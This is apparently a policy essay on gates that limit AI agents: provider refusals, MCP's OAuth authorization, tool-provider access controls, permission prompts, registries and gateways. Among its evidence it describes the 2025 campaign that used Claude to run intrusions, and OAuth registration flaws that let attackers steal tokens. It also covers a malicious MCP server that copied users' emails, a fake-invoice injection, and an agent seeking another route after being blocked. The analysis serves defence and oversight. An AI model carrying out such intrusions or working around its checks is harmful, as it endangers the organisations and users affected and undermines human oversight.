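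A provider's refusal withholds more from attackers the further its model is ahead of others. In April 2026 Anthropic gave a small group of organisations early access to its strongest model, through Project Glasswing, so that they could fix flaws in critical software. Anthropic's *Bringing the cybersecurity capabilities of Claude Mythos 5 to more defenders* (2026) describes the benefit as a "window of time" before similar models became generally available or reached malicious actors. So Anthropic expected the gate to delay attackers rather than keep them out permanently.

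### The espionage campaign of 2025

In mid-September 2025 Anthropic detected an operation that used Claude Code to break into organisations' computers, which it attributed to a Chinese state-sponsored group. Anthropic's *Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (2025) says the group targeted roughly 30 organisations, including technology companies, banks, chemical manufacturers and government agencies, and succeeded in a handful of cases.

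The group had connected Claude to several specialised MCP servers. One let it run commands on remote machines equipped for penetration testing (authorised attempts to break into a system). Others controlled a web browser, analysed code, linked Claude to testing software and checked whether an attack had worked. The tools behind these servers were mostly open-source security programs, and the group mainly wrote code to connect them.

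Anthropic estimates that Claude did 80 to 90% of the tactical work. People chose the targets and approved the important steps, such as moving from surveying a network to attacking it. In one example, Claude worked for one to four hours and the human operator for two to ten minutes. So the attackers ran their own autonomy gate, presumably because they didn't trust the agent either. They had some reason for distrust, since Claude sometimes claimed to have obtained credentials that didn't work.

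Anthropic gives no start date for the campaign, but some of Claude's sessions lasted several days, and at the campaign's peak Claude was making several requests a second. Each task looked legitimate by itself, but the sustained activity eventually triggered detection. Over the next ten days Anthropic traced the operation, banned accounts as it identified them, notified the organisations affected and worked with the authorities. Afterwards it improved its classifiers for cyberattacks and began work on earlier detection.

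Both sides of the debate can cite this case. Nobody could have stopped the group from building its servers, but when Anthropic closed the accounts, it cut Claude off from all of those servers at once without touching them. No other party could have done that. However, Anthropic acted after some of the break-ins had succeeded. Closing accounts that late may still prevent further break-ins, but it does little for the companies already breached. Anthropic also found signs that the group had already passed its access to other teams, who wouldn't have needed Claude to use it.

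Anthropic also could not tell whether the group moved to another company's model, because it sees only Claude usage. It suspects that attackers use other leading models in similar ways.

### Where the provider sees less

A provider has to store requests to notice a pattern across many of them. Anthropic's *Data retention practices for Mythos-class models* gives espionage as an example of misuse that becomes visible only when classifiers can examine many requests together. Some business customers had agreements under which Anthropic stored nothing, but from 9 June 2026 it required 30 days of storage for Mythos-class models, which include Fable, on every platform that offers them. Staff can read a conversation only if it has been flagged for potential serious harm or the customer asks in writing, and Anthropic normally deletes the data after the 30 days.

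Anthropic exempts some organisations from the rule, and customers who reach Claude through Amazon's or Google's cloud keep the stored data in that cloud. In August, *Claude Fable 5 data retention may move to your cloud, not vanish* (Popular AI, 2026) relayed a Reuters report that Anthropic planned to let business customers hold the required data in their own cloud systems. A classifier can still check each request as it arrives, but an investigator would find it harder to trace a campaign across several customers' clouds.

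Providers can respond by giving fewer permissions to customers they can't monitor as well. Amazon Bedrock, a cloud service that resells Claude, doesn't yet support human review of automated safety flags, so Anthropic keeps most Bedrock customers out of the Cyber Verification Program. However, it makes exceptions for organisations exempt from data storage, so a few customers get looser safeguards with less monitoring. Botcrawl reports that OpenAI similarly warned of limits on access to an earlier model, GPT-5.4-Cyber, for customers who store no data and for those who come through other companies' platforms. Both providers could therefore close much of this gap through their contracts, but they might lose customers who won't accept the terms.

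A contract does less about tool calls that the model writes as code. Suppose a business wants an agent to send reminders about unpaid invoices. In the ordinary loop, the model requests the list of invoices, reads it and then writes a separate request for each email. With 500 emails to send, the provider receives 500 addresses and 500 messages. The model could instead write a short program:

```python
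sent = 0
for invoice in list_invoices():
    if invoice.days_overdue > 30:
        send_email(invoice.customer, "Payment reminder", reminder_text)
        sent += 1
print(sent)
```

If the host application runs this program on the customer's machine, the provider receives the program, because the model wrote it, and the number it prints at the end, but not the invoices or the addresses. This saves developers time and money because the model doesn't have to read or write 500 emails. But the provider now has one chance to refuse instead of 500. It can judge what the program is for, but it can't check whether the people on the list are customers. If the code runs on the provider's own machines, as it does with some of Anthropic's code tools, the provider can watch the calls as they happen.

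False descriptions cause a similar problem. If a developer tells the model that a live payment system is a test version, both the model and the provider's classifiers will assess a real payment as if it were a test. Verification helps a little, because if a bank later reports the fraud, the provider will know which customer to suspend.

### Choosing among applications

A provider that can't see everything an application does could still accept only the applications it trusts. Anthropic spent much of 2026 limiting the host applications that other developers write to run Claude in a loop, though these limits had more to do with money than with trust.

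A Claude subscription costs a fixed amount each month, whereas the API charges for each unit of text. Some outside programs, including the coding agent OpenCode, had been connecting through users' subscriptions by presenting themselves to Anthropic's servers as Claude Code. In January Anthropic blocked them. VentureBeat's *Anthropic cracks down on unauthorized Claude usage by third-party harnesses* reports that the Anthropic engineer Thariq Shihipar blamed bugs and usage patterns that the company couldn't diagnose. According to Acidbath's *Anthropic crackdown*, he also said that such programs sent none of the "usual telemetry" that Claude Code provides. The lack of visibility is a fair complaint, but users pointed to cost, and one estimated that a month of heavy subscription use could easily have cost more than $1,000 through the API.

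The policy then changed several times:

- From 4 April, subscriptions no longer covered outside agent programs, starting with one called OpenClaw. In an email that a user posted as *Tell HN*, Anthropic told customers they could pay for that use separately.
- In May Anthropic announced a monthly credit for outside programs, worth $20 to $200 depending on the plan, according to VentureBeat's *Anthropic reinstates OpenClaw and third-party agent usage on Claude subscriptions*.
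- On 15 June it paused the change. Anthropic's *Use the Claude Agent SDK with your Claude plan* stated that outside applications still drew on subscription limits. Three weeks later, however, Invidious Musings' *Anthropic's Method to Losing Goodwill in a Few Easy Steps* (2026) reproduced a warning in one such program that Anthropic would bill its use separately.

Throughout, outside developers could connect their programs to the paid API. Anthropic's *Legal and compliance* tells them to use it and forbids them from offering Claude subscription logins in their own products. So Anthropic was withholding a discount, and anyone willing to pay full price could still connect a program.

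The January block does show how well a provider can enforce a rule about applications. Anthropic could recognise and refuse the programs, although its filters also banned some accounts by mistake. But within hours OpenCode let its users sign in with a ChatGPT subscription instead, and it launched a $200-a-month plan that reportedly reached Claude through the API. Substitutes were easy to find for everyday coding, but they would be much scarcer for work that only one or two models can do.

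The episode also strengthens an objection about competition. Anthropic sells Claude Code, so any company whose rival coding agent runs on Claude is both its customer and its competitor. In *To unleash AI innovation, stop model providers from picking the winners*, a Brookings Institution commentary, Ramzanali and Wheeler (2026) compare the leading models to railways and telephone networks, which governments required to serve all customers on equal terms. They want to bar model providers from unjust discrimination in price, speed or quality, and from cutting off a customer because it competes with them.

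People who make this case mainly cite Windsurf, a coding tool. In mid-2025, after reports that OpenAI might buy the company, Anthropic cut off nearly all of Windsurf's direct access to Claude with less than a week's notice. An Anthropic co-founder explained that it would be "odd" to sell Claude to a company on its way to joining a rival. Anthropic restored access for Windsurf's paying users some weeks later. VentureBeat reports that Anthropic also revoked OpenAI's access that August, and that its commercial terms forbid customers to use Claude to build competing products.

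This matters for autonomy gates because a provider that profits from refusing to serve a rival can easily call the refusal a safety measure. Outsiders can't readily check that claim, since the provider holds the evidence of misuse.

The safety reply is that a provider has to treat applications differently, because some are far more dangerous than others. Anthropic argues that the risk is greatest when a user has direct access to the model and can try to steer it. If a product runs Mythos in the background and returns only a suggested repair for a flaw, its user cannot ask for an attack. A rule that forced Anthropic to offer Mythos on the same terms to that product and to an open chat window would remove the gate.

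The reply is sound, but Anthropic's own product benefited from the distinction. Claude Security, which scans a customer's code for flaws and requires a person to approve every repair, began running on Mythos 5 on 21 August 2026. Anthropic said at the time that it was working with selected partners to build the model into their products. In early October, other companies that wanted to build products through the verification program could still only register their interest. Anthropic has since opened applications, but only for defensive products whose customers can't direct the model or see its raw output. OpenAI's rules are simpler and stricter, since they forbid approved customers from passing trusted access on to any outside users.

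A head start of several weeks probably reflects both caution and self-interest. The two positions are compatible in principle. A provider could publish the conditions for each kind of application and apply them to its own products, and Anthropic's categories are already a step towards this. Such a rule would forbid cutting off Windsurf over a possible sale but allow keeping Mythos out of an open chat window. Someone would still have to judge disputed refusals, and Ramzanali and Wheeler leave open who that should be.

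## The case that the gate passes to tool providers

An agent can take money out of a bank account only if the bank carries out the transfer. The bank can refuse whether the instruction came from Claude, a model running on a laptop or an accounting program. The same goes for a mailbox or a company's customer records, because whoever controls a service decides which requests it accepts. On this view, open standards left the gate with the tool providers, most of whom were deciding which programs to admit long before MCP.

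FBT Gibbons, an American law firm, says that a purchase by a shopping agent can be legally valid, with a clear record that the customer authorised it, and still fail because the merchant, the platform or the payment company won't deal with the agent.

### Why defend downstream

*AI safety is not a model property*, a March 2024 essay by the computer scientists Arvind Narayanan and Sayash Kapoor, makes the general argument. It compares building a model that nobody can misuse to building "a computer that can't be used for bad things" (quoted by Harvard's Berkman Klein Center, 2024). Whether a use is harmful usually depends on facts that the model doesn't have. Suppose someone asks for a short, urgent email telling staff to open an attachment. The model can't tell what the attachment contains or who will send the email, but the mail host can scan the attachment, check the sender's address and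 notice that 4,000 people are getting the same message. So defences belong mainly with the services that an attack has to pass through.

*AI safety is sometimes a model property*, a reply from May 2024, accepts several of these points but rejects the blanket conclusion, since some measures make sense in the model and others in the system around it. The Knight First Amendment Institute's *A Conceptual Model to Guide AI Risk Governance Strategies* finds many of Narayanan and Kapoor's criticisms compelling, but records the view that some outputs are harmful in themselves and that the developer can stop those most efficiently. Instructions for making a weapon, for example, do harm as soon as somebody reads them, so a bank or mail host has no chance to intervene.

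That objection has less force against tool gates. An agent's action has to happen somewhere, usually on a machine that somebody else owns.

### How a remote server lets an agent in

Many online services admit other companies' programs through OAuth, a standard that lets a person give a program limited access to an account without handing over the password. The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) applies OAuth to remote MCP servers. Suppose a mail company runs its own MCP server, and someone connects an assistant to it for the first time:

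1. The host application's client sends a request without an access token. The server rejects it with error 401 and points the client to a page describing how to log in. It will usually name the scope the client needs, such as `mail:read`.
2. The client finds the login system, which MCP calls the authorization server. The mail company may run this itself or use another firm's.
3. The client gets an ID there. The two companies may have arranged one in advance, or the client can give the web address of a document that describes it. Older systems let it register on the spot, which is known as dynamic client registration.
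4. The client makes up a one-time secret and opens the login page in the user's browser. The link carries a scrambled version of the secret, the scopes the client wants and the address of the one MCP server where it will use the token.
5. The user signs in, reads what the program is asking for, and approves or declines.
6. The login system sends the browser back to the client with a code. The client trades the code and the original secret for an access token. The secret shows that the program collecting the token is the one that started the login.
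7. The client attaches the token to every later request. Each time, the server must check that the token is valid and that the login system issued it for this server.

The model takes no part in this exchange, so nothing it outputs can make the mail server accept a token that lacks the right scope.

The mail company can refuse at almost every step. It can decline to register the client, turn it away at login or reject any single call. It can also narrow what it grants. If the user approved reading only, and the agent later tries to send a message, the server returns something like this:

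```http
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer error="insufficient_scope", scope="mail:send"
```

Refusing an agent's request because it lacks a scope doesn't settle the matter, since MCP recommends that the client send the user back to the login page to ask for the missing scope. The user may well click "approve" to get the job done, so a company that wants a firm limit on sending email has to stop offering the `mail:send` scope to agents at all.

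Tokens also expire, and the Model Context Protocol recommends short lifetimes to limit the damage if one leaks. To continue without a new login, the client needs a refresh token, a second credential that the login system can withhold. A bank could therefore issue one-hour tokens without refresh tokens, so a person would have to sign in every hour for the agent to continue. This would limit how long the agent could run unsupervised, which a model provider can do only crudely with usage caps.

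Finally, the company can revoke a token. If its server checks every token with the login system, the agent's next call fails. If the server only checks the token's digital signature, the agent can keep making calls until the token expires.

### Holding a message until somebody reads it

A scope gives the user only coarse control, because the user approves it once and the agent may then send 500 emails. But a tool provider can enforce the rule that the model provider could not, that no agent may send mail from a person's account until that person has read the message. The mail host can accept the agent's message as a draft, show it to the user on its own website and send it only after the user approves. Some banks already do something similar by asking customers to confirm unusual transfers in the bank's app.

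Zhu, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *OpenPort Protocol*, propose a standard way to build this. Their design puts a gateway in front of the service and treats the model as untrustworthy. The gateway denies everything that the operator hasn't explicitly allowed, and it doesn't even show the agent tools it may not use:

VisibleTools(a) = { t : ReqScopes(t) ⊆ Scopes(a) and PolicyAllows(a, t) }

Application *a* sees tool *t* only if it holds all the scopes that *t* requires and the operator's policy permits it. An agent with scopes for reading and drafting would see the reading and drafting tools but have no sign that a sending tool exists.

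Any request to change something becomes a draft by default, and a person approves or rejects it. This creates a new risk, that the agent gets approval for one action and then carries out another. For risky actions, the gateway can therefore compute a fingerprint of the request beforehand:

h = H(C(t, x, I(t, x)))

Here *x* stands for the tool's arguments and *I* for the effect the server expects them to have. *C* writes all this in a fixed format, and *H* turns it into a short code that changes if any detail changes. If the agent previews a payment of £200 to Ravi and then submits one with a different account number, the codes don't match and the server must refuse. An optional check covers delays. If a manager approves an invoice but a colleague pays it before the approved payment goes through, the server detects that the account has changed and blocks the second payment.

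The design assumes that the gateway is the only way in, so an agent that can reach the database directly bypasses all of these checks. Zhu and colleagues also assume that the administrator is honest. Both assumptions are reasonable for a bank but less safe for a small firm where the agent runs on the same machine as the accounts.

### From no rules to one token per service

MCP's rules on all this have changed in every revision:

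| Revision | Main change to authorization |
|---|---|
| November 2024 | No mandatory authentication for remote servers |
| March 2025 | A framework based on OAuth 2.1 |
| June 2025 | A separate login system issues tokens, each for one server |
| November 2025 | Clients preferably identify themselves with a web address |
| July 2026 | Clients check which login system answered, and dynamic registration starts its phase-out |

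Bucknall and colleagues describe OAuth as an optional feature of the March 2025 version, while Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, call it the mandatory framework. The later versions suggest that both can be right, because a developer may leave authorization out, but any login system that takes part must use OAuth 2.1.

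The June 2025 change matters most for gates. Parecki (2025), summarising it on the day of its release, explained that MCP servers no longer had to issue tokens or log users in, because a dedicated system would do both. Clients also had to name the server they wanted a token for, a rule the Model Context Protocol introduced to stop malicious servers from obtaining tokens. Suppose an agent uses both a mail server and a horoscope server. Without the rule, the horoscope server could trick the client into getting a token from the mail company's login page and handing it over, then use it to read the mail. The rule prevents this by making the token work only at the horoscope server, but only if the login system supports the feature, according to the Model Context Protocol.

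The July 2026 revision deals with a related trick, in which a client that connects to many login systems sends one system's code to an attacker's. Model Context Protocol (2026), announcing the release candidate, explained that such mix-ups are more common when one client deals with many servers. Clients must now check the issuer's name when a login system supplies it, and they must keep credentials from one login system away from every other. Tabata (2026), in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, points out that none of these ideas is new to OAuth, which is reassuring because companies that already run OAuth know how to manage them.

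Authorization is still optional, but whoever runs the server decides whether to require it, and a client can't opt out of a token that the server requires. Optional authorization therefore weakens the gate only where a provider doesn't require it.

### How many servers check

Many fail to. Zhou and colleagues took 28,715 candidate addresses from FOFA and Shodan, two search engines for internet-connected machines, and sent each an MCP greeting. They identified 7,973 live MCP servers. They checked 100 of these by hand and found that all but one were real.

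| What the server asked for | Servers | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 3,233 | 40.55% |
| A fixed key or token | 2,312 | 29.00% |
| An OAuth login | 2,428 | 30.45% |

This is the best available measurement of servers with no authentication. *Exposed by Design* (Padilla, 2026) reports that 91.8% of 414 servers tested in July 2026 lacked OAuth. The comparable figure from Zhou and colleagues is about 70%. Servers that ask for a fixed key also lack OAuth, so the 91.8% figure doesn't mean that nine in ten were open to anyone.

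Open servers are often unimportant. Zhou and colleagues inspected a random selection, and most were tests or demonstrations with no sensitive data. Padilla found that 41.6% of 464 servers had disappeared three days later, which also suggests that many were hobby projects. However, one server in the first study let anyone search more than 5,000 customer records, because a company had put an internal system online without a login. Neither study weights servers by how many people use them, and both miss servers on private networks. Roughly two in five publicly visible servers had no gate, but they could therefore handle a far smaller share of agent activity.

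A server can have a login that doesn't work. To test OAuth itself, Zhou and colleagues needed servers they could log in to without arranging access with each owner, so they considered only the 1,118 that advertised dynamic registration. They had 119 left after removing duplicates, broken servers, 316 servers behind corporate access controls, and some others. They connected to these with VS Code Copilot, a coding assistant, and recorded the traffic. Then they altered requests to see what the login systems would accept, and confirmed each flaw by hand.

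All 119 servers had at least one flaw, and 115 (96.6%) had a flaw in client registration. In 114 cases, the login system let an anonymous program register any return address. An attacker could register a program with their own address and send someone a link to the service's genuine login page. If that person signed in and approved, the login system would send the attacker a code they could exchange for a token.

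The 96.6% is weak evidence about MCP servers in general, because the researchers selected servers with the feature that contains the flaw. The 114 servers are 4.7% of the OAuth servers they found. A server without dynamic registration can't have this flaw, so at most about 46% of the OAuth servers could have it. The true share is between those two figures, which is still bad for a login system.

The theft is only part of the problem for an autonomy gate. If anybody can register a program under any name, the service can't keep a list of approved agents, so it fails the test of seeing the connection. Identification by web address helps, because others can't easily forge a document at a company's own address. It works less well for desktop programs, which receive the login code on the user's machine, where another program can impersonate them.

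The remedies are mostly configuration changes. Zhou and colleagues recommend restricting return addresses and rejecting logins that lack a properly scrambled one-time secret. Of the 119 servers, 81 accepted such logins. But small providers often lack the skill to make these changes. According to Bucknall and colleagues, dynamic registration was too demanding for server developers, many of whom didn't know how to implement it correctly. They compare MCP's position with the web's slow move to encrypted connections. The standard for these came out in 2000, yet in 2017 half of the most popular websites still used unencrypted connections by default. Free certificates, browser warnings and a US government mandate for federal sites made encryption common. If the comparison holds, safer defaults in MCP's code libraries would improve security more than another revision of the rules.

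### Refusals in practice

Large companies exclude agents when they want to. FBT Gibbons distinguishes three ways to control access: excluding agents outright, admitting them on conditions, and requiring them to use a particular route, such as an approved API.

Boulos (2025), in *Digital Freedom Depends on Access Rights*, reports that Salesforce, which owns the workplace chat service Slack, changed its contract terms to stop companies such as Glean, which makes an AI search tool, from using Slack data. Slack can see which programs use its API and cut them off, and a company's chat history is hard to find anywhere else, so the restriction passes all three tests of enforceability. It doesn't look like an autonomy gate, though, because nothing in Boulos's account suggests that Glean could regain access by showing that its software was safe.

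According to FBT Gibbons, Visa's Token Service and Mastercard's Delegated Authentication both build conditions on credentials into the card network, so those conditions apply before any merchant sees the request. A payment token stands in for the card number, and a network can restrict its use. An agent might be able to spend only up to a set amount, or only at certain shops, until its user approves more.

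A card network can enforce a gate more effectively than any single shop. An agent turned away by one grocer can order from another, but most grocers accept the same few cards. The agent could try a bank transfer instead, but then the bank would hold the gate. The network's control is weakest when an agent types an ordinary card number into a checkout page as a person would, because the agent presents no special credential for the network to check.

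### What a tool provider cannot see

A bank might reasonably want to admit only agents whose models have passed a safety test, but it has no good way to do so. Since July 2026 the Model Context Protocol has recommended that clients identify themselves in every request, but clients give the application's name, not the model's, and an application can claim any name. Tool providers can set conditions on the user, the action and the amount far more easily than on the model.

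Intermediaries hide even more. Of the 119 servers that Zhou and colleagues tested, 81 used the user's permission to reach another company's service. That company sees the intermediary's ID and the user's account, but not necessarily the application using the intermediary. It can cancel one user's permission or block the intermediary for everyone, but it may be unable to exclude one kind of agent.

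No tool provider sees all the tools an agent has either. Suppose a stranger emails a fake invoice to someone whose agent handles their bills, and the agent pays it. The mail host sees an agent reading mail, as the user allowed, and the bank sees a valid token and a payment below the limit. Only the host application and the model provider can see that the instruction to pay came from a stranger. Even with only part of the evidence, the bank could still catch the fraud if it knew the receiving account was fraudulent, or if it held every payment to a new recipient for approval.

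A service is similarly unable to detect a stolen token, because the thief's requests look legitimate. Requests from a corrupted tool can look legitimate too. Bucknall and colleagues describe an unofficial MCP server for Postmark, an email-sending company, which worked normally for 15 versions and then began secretly copying users' emails to an outside address. Postmark would presumably have seen only properly authorised messages with one extra recipient.

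Providers also differ in how much reason they have to check what an agent is doing. A bank that may have to refund a fraudulent payment has good reason to examine it. Mail hosts police spam partly because other hosts will block them if they don't. But a cloud company that rents servers to an agent gets paid whatever the agent does with them, at least until somebody complains. *The Loss of Control Playbook* treats the power to acquire computing resources as one of the more dangerous affordances, yet the company that could deny an agent those resources earns money by providing them. A victim who has no contract with the cloud company can't easily make it refuse the agent.

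The strength of the gate therefore varies a great deal with the affordance:

| Affordance | Who can refuse | What the agent can do instead |
|---|---|---|
| Paying from a particular bank account | The bank | Almost nothing |
| Reading a company's Slack messages | Slack | Look for exported copies |
| Renting a server | Each cloud company | Try another company |
| Emailing strangers | Each mail host | Try another host |
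| Deleting files on a laptop | No outside provider | No need for a substitute |

The argument applies only partly to the last row, because local MCP servers don't use the login process. Under MCP's rules, they should take their credentials from the machine they run on, and a tool that edits files may need none. If a local server connects to a bank, the bank can still refuse access, but for anything confined to the machine, only the user, the host application or an employer that manages the computer can enforce the gate.

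### Whether users have a right to bring an agent

Boulos objects that tool providers refuse agents too often. He is head of policy at Imbue, which builds agent tools, so he has a commercial interest, but the complaint is serious. An airline can use AI to set the highest fare a customer will pay, and an agent could shop around on the customer's behalf. If the airline or the booking site can block that agent, only one side gets to use AI. His example is Amazon, which blocks ChatGPT and other AI tools. FBT Gibbons adds that Amazon is developing Buy for Me, an agent that shops on other merchants' sites, while fighting in court to keep a rival's shopping agent off its own site.

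Boulos wants people to have a legal right to access their own data and the systems they depend on, using any software they choose. He argues that existing law is inadequate. Antitrust law deals with abuses of monopoly, but here a whole industry habitually refuses access. Discrimination law doesn't help either, because it protects particular groups and these refusals affect everyone. He points to the ACCESS Act, a bipartisan bill in the US Senate, which would require large platforms to build interfaces that outside agents could use to examine and potentially remove personal data.

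Services have a safety case for refusing agents, because they often bear the loss when an agent goes wrong. FBT Gibbons accepts that fraud, user protection and the handling of disputes can all justify controls on agents. If the law forced a bank to accept every agent that a customer chose, the bank could no longer hold back an unreliable one, and the most enforceable gate in this section would disappear. Refusal can also protect other people. A Slack channel contains everyone's messages, so one employee's right to their own data doesn't settle whether their agent may copy the whole conversation. Boulos traces the first draft of the ACCESS Act to the Cambridge Analytica scandal, in which a political consultancy improperly obtained data on millions of Facebook users, most of whom had never used the app that collected it but had friends who did.

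The same history shows that a right of access can have conditions, since Boulos stresses that the bill's drafters left platforms free to protect their users. OAuth also reduces the conflict because users don't have to hand over their passwords. A right of access could require a service to admit a customer's agent but still let the service limit the agent's scopes, require approval for large payments and revoke its token after misconduct. Revocations would be the hard cases, because a platform that sells its own agent could use claims of misconduct to shut out rivals. FBT Gibbons advises companies that restrict agents to record whether their real reason is safety or competition. A company with a bad reason is unlikely to record it candidly, so a right of access would need someone outside the company to hear appeals.

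## The case for gates in applications, registries and workplaces

Without a shared standard, connecting 10 applications to 200 tools would take 2,000 custom connectors, and anyone checking agents' tool calls would have to understand 2,000 formats. Every MCP call has the same layout, a tool's name and a list of arguments, so one program can read all of them and block those that break a rule. On this view, the standard makes tools easier to inspect as well as to connect. Whoever controls the software between the agent and the tools would then run the gate, such as the maker of the host application, the operator of a registry or an employer.

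### Asking the user

The simplest checkpoint is a prompt for the user's approval before the application carries out a call. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes how the company's coding agent originally asked for approval before it ran a command or changed a file. Users could also write rules to allow or block particular tools, commands and MCP servers, or to require approval for them.

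Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that users accepted 97% of permission prompts. Most of the commands were probably harmless, so that figure alone doesn't show carelessness, but an experiment in the same article does. A research vendor hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Of the testers, 143 (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. An automatic classifier that Anthropic built to review calls blocked 89% of the same commands.

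The testers worked in a practice environment, so they may have been less careful than with their own files. Anthropic also has a commercial interest in the result, since it sells the product and says that people who use the classifier complete more work. But other researchers describe the same habit. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that user review contributed to 105 of the 290 reports it examined, and in 80 of those the user had set the agent to run without asking. In 31, the prompt gave the user too little information. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it lets the agent run whatever code the file contains. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed 115 for *Let the Agent Do It?*, and they warn designers not to treat repeated approvals as a stable preference.

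People did better in a study by Yan (2026), *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* The 113 participants, none from the software industry, supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven actions went beyond what the user had asked for, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass or reading private messages. Yan compared three designs:

| Who decided | Unrequested actions blocked | Prompts per person |
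|---|---|---|
| The user, on every action | 59.6% | 18 |
| A model, which passed doubtful actions to the user | 53.9% | 10 |
| Rules the user wrote in advance | 39.6% | 10.9 |

These participants only had to judge requests written in plain language, whereas Anthropic's testers were trying to finish a coding task. That probably explains much of the gap between 59.6% and 13.6%. Some approvals were also sensible. For example, nearly everyone let the agent call the airport to confirm a flight, which counted as overreach because nobody had asked for it.

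Rules written in advance had a surprisingly weak effect. Participants could choose "allow", "ask" or "never" for each kind of action, and they chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules. They then approved two thirds of the unrequested actions they were asked about. An "ask" rule postpones the decision until the user is busiest, so it doesn't commit them to refusing.

Asking users to make fewer, larger decisions may work better. Claude Code's users reject 39% of the plans it shows them before starting work, compared with 3% of its individual requests. They may be rejecting the approach rather than a danger, but they are reading the plans. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) notes that Devin, another coding agent, asks for approval of its plan and again when it submits the finished code.

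On 14 August 2026, Anthropic made a classifier the default reviewer of calls in new Claude Code sessions on most of its subscription plans. If the classifier blocks three calls in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. Even after Anthropic strengthened it, the classifier missed 7% of the attacks that Apollo Research, an AI safety company, had designed to defeat it. It also can't satisfy a rule that a person must read every email before an agent sends it, because its purpose is to let the agent act without a person reading each call.

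### Registries and directories

A checkpoint can also come earlier, when the user picks a server. Companies that make host applications offer directories of connectors, and MCP's maintainers run an official registry. Since people mostly install a small number of popular servers, a carefully vetted catalogue could protect most users.

Current registries don't check much. Bucknall and colleagues report that the official one relies on its community to moderate entries and has put off scanning source code until a later version. OX Security's *The Mother of All AI Supply Chains* says that the company's researchers got a malicious test server into nine of 11 registries. OX sells security products, so it has a reason to find such problems, but the result is plausible given how little registries check.

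A strict catalogue of servers becomes a gate only when the application or the machine blocks everything unlisted. Otherwise, users can connect an unlisted server by pasting in its address. For years, for example, ordinary iPhone owners could install apps only from Apple's store, so Apple's refusal kept an app off their phones. The NSA's May 2026 guidance suggests a version of this in which organisations review servers before adopting them, run them on their own machines where possible, and enrol them in a registry for internal use.

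### Locking down the machine

A local MCP server starts with much the same permissions as the application that launched it. If that application can read the user's tax returns, the server usually can too. The Model Context Protocol's *Security Policy* warns that the local connection "is not a sandbox", meaning it doesn't confine the server, and leaves isolation to whoever sets up the machine.

Operating systems can already do this. The NSA recommends treating any tool execution as potentially high-risk and running each tool inside a restriction such as AppContainer on Windows or AppArmor on Linux. An administrator could let a note-taking server open one folder and deny it network access. If the server tries to send email despite its description, the attempt fails, because the operating system checks what the program does rather than how it is described. These restrictions put a gate on purely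 local actions, such as deleting files, which no tool provider can refuse. They also need maintenance. As Anthropic points out, each new capability needs configuring, and many useful tools need the network.

The NSA also advises organisations to keep an inventory of the servers they run and scan their networks for others, such as those a developer installed without permission. Scans have to be regular because servers can change ports, the numbered channels on which they accept connections. A scan finds a server after somebody has installed it, so enforcing an approved list requires another control that stops unapproved servers from doing anything.

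### One blocked call

A gateway can provide that control. Suppose a company routes its agents' MCP traffic through one, and an employee asks an agent to send Ravi the customer list. The agent finds the wrong Ravi, who works for a competitor.

1. Before any of this, the host application asked for the mail server's list of tools. The gateway fetched it, scanned the descriptions for hidden instructions and passed it on.
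2. The model requests `send_email`. The application sends the call to the gateway, which sits in front of the mail server:

```json
{
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "send_email",
    "arguments": {
      "to": "ravi@competitor.example",
      "subject": "Customer list",
      "body": "Here are all 5,000 customers: ..."
    }
  }
}
```

3. The gateway compares the call with the company's rules. One says that an agent may email outside addresses only with a manager's approval.
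4. The gateway records the attempt and returns an error. The mail server never receives the call.
5. The application adds the error to the conversation, and the model reads that outside recipients need approval.

The agent may then ask the employee what to do or look for another way. In one case inside Anthropic, Claude couldn't upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. The classifier stopped it. A gateway that covered only email would have missed an attempt like that, so the NSA also recommends a filter on all outgoing connections.

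Microsoft released an open-source gateway of this kind, the Agent Governance Toolkit, and described it in an April 2026 post. It applies fixed rules, so the same call always gets the same answer, and Microsoft says a typical check takes less than a millisecond. It also gives each agent an identity and a trust score from 0 to 1,000, which falls when the agent breaks a rule and can recover with good behaviour. A company that tied permissions to the score would have a true autonomy gate, because agents would have to earn permissions through good behaviour.

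There is less evidence on how well gateways work. Microsoft tested agents that had only written instructions to follow the rules, and more than a quarter of its 45 adversarial prompts succeeded. That result is a good reason not to rely on instructions, but the test included no gateway, so it doesn't show how well one would work.

In a better test, Yan built a gateway that used a language model to sort tools by consequence, such as spending or deleting, and then forwarded each call, asked the user or blocked it. When Yan simulated a "never" rule for each kind of action, the gateway failed to block 14% of the tools it should have blocked and blocked 4% of those it should have allowed. Asking the user about uncertain cases cut the misses to 11%. Yan concludes that the sorting isn't reliable enough to be a security boundary by itself. The tools in this test had ordinary descriptions, not deliberately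 misleading ones.

The argument from a common format has a weakness, because MCP standardises how a call looks but a gateway also has to know what the tool does. The problem is much smaller for a company with 20 approved servers than for a consumer who might connect to any of thousands. The company's staff can read the code and label each tool by hand, although they must do it again whenever a tool changes.

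Gateways can also miss harm that builds up over several calls. An agent might read a salary file, summarise it and post the summary in a public channel, all through calls that the rules individually allow. Microsoft says its toolkit can't yet connect such steps. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) proposes approval screens that link each request to the earlier actions it builds on, though that would return the decision to a tired reviewer. The NSA considers gateways that can parse MCP traffic limited and still maturing, and advises caution where data is sensitive.

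### The employer's login system

Employees normally decide whether to connect an agent to a server by clicking "approve" on the service's login page. Enterprise-managed authorization moves that decision to the employer. The organisation's identity provider, the system staff use to sign in to their work accounts, controls which MCP servers they may reach (McCaffrey, 2026, *MCP Graduates to Enterprise Infrastructure*). An employer could let the accounts department connect agents to the invoicing system and refuse everyone else. Staff also get a simpler login, which gives them a reason to use the approved route.

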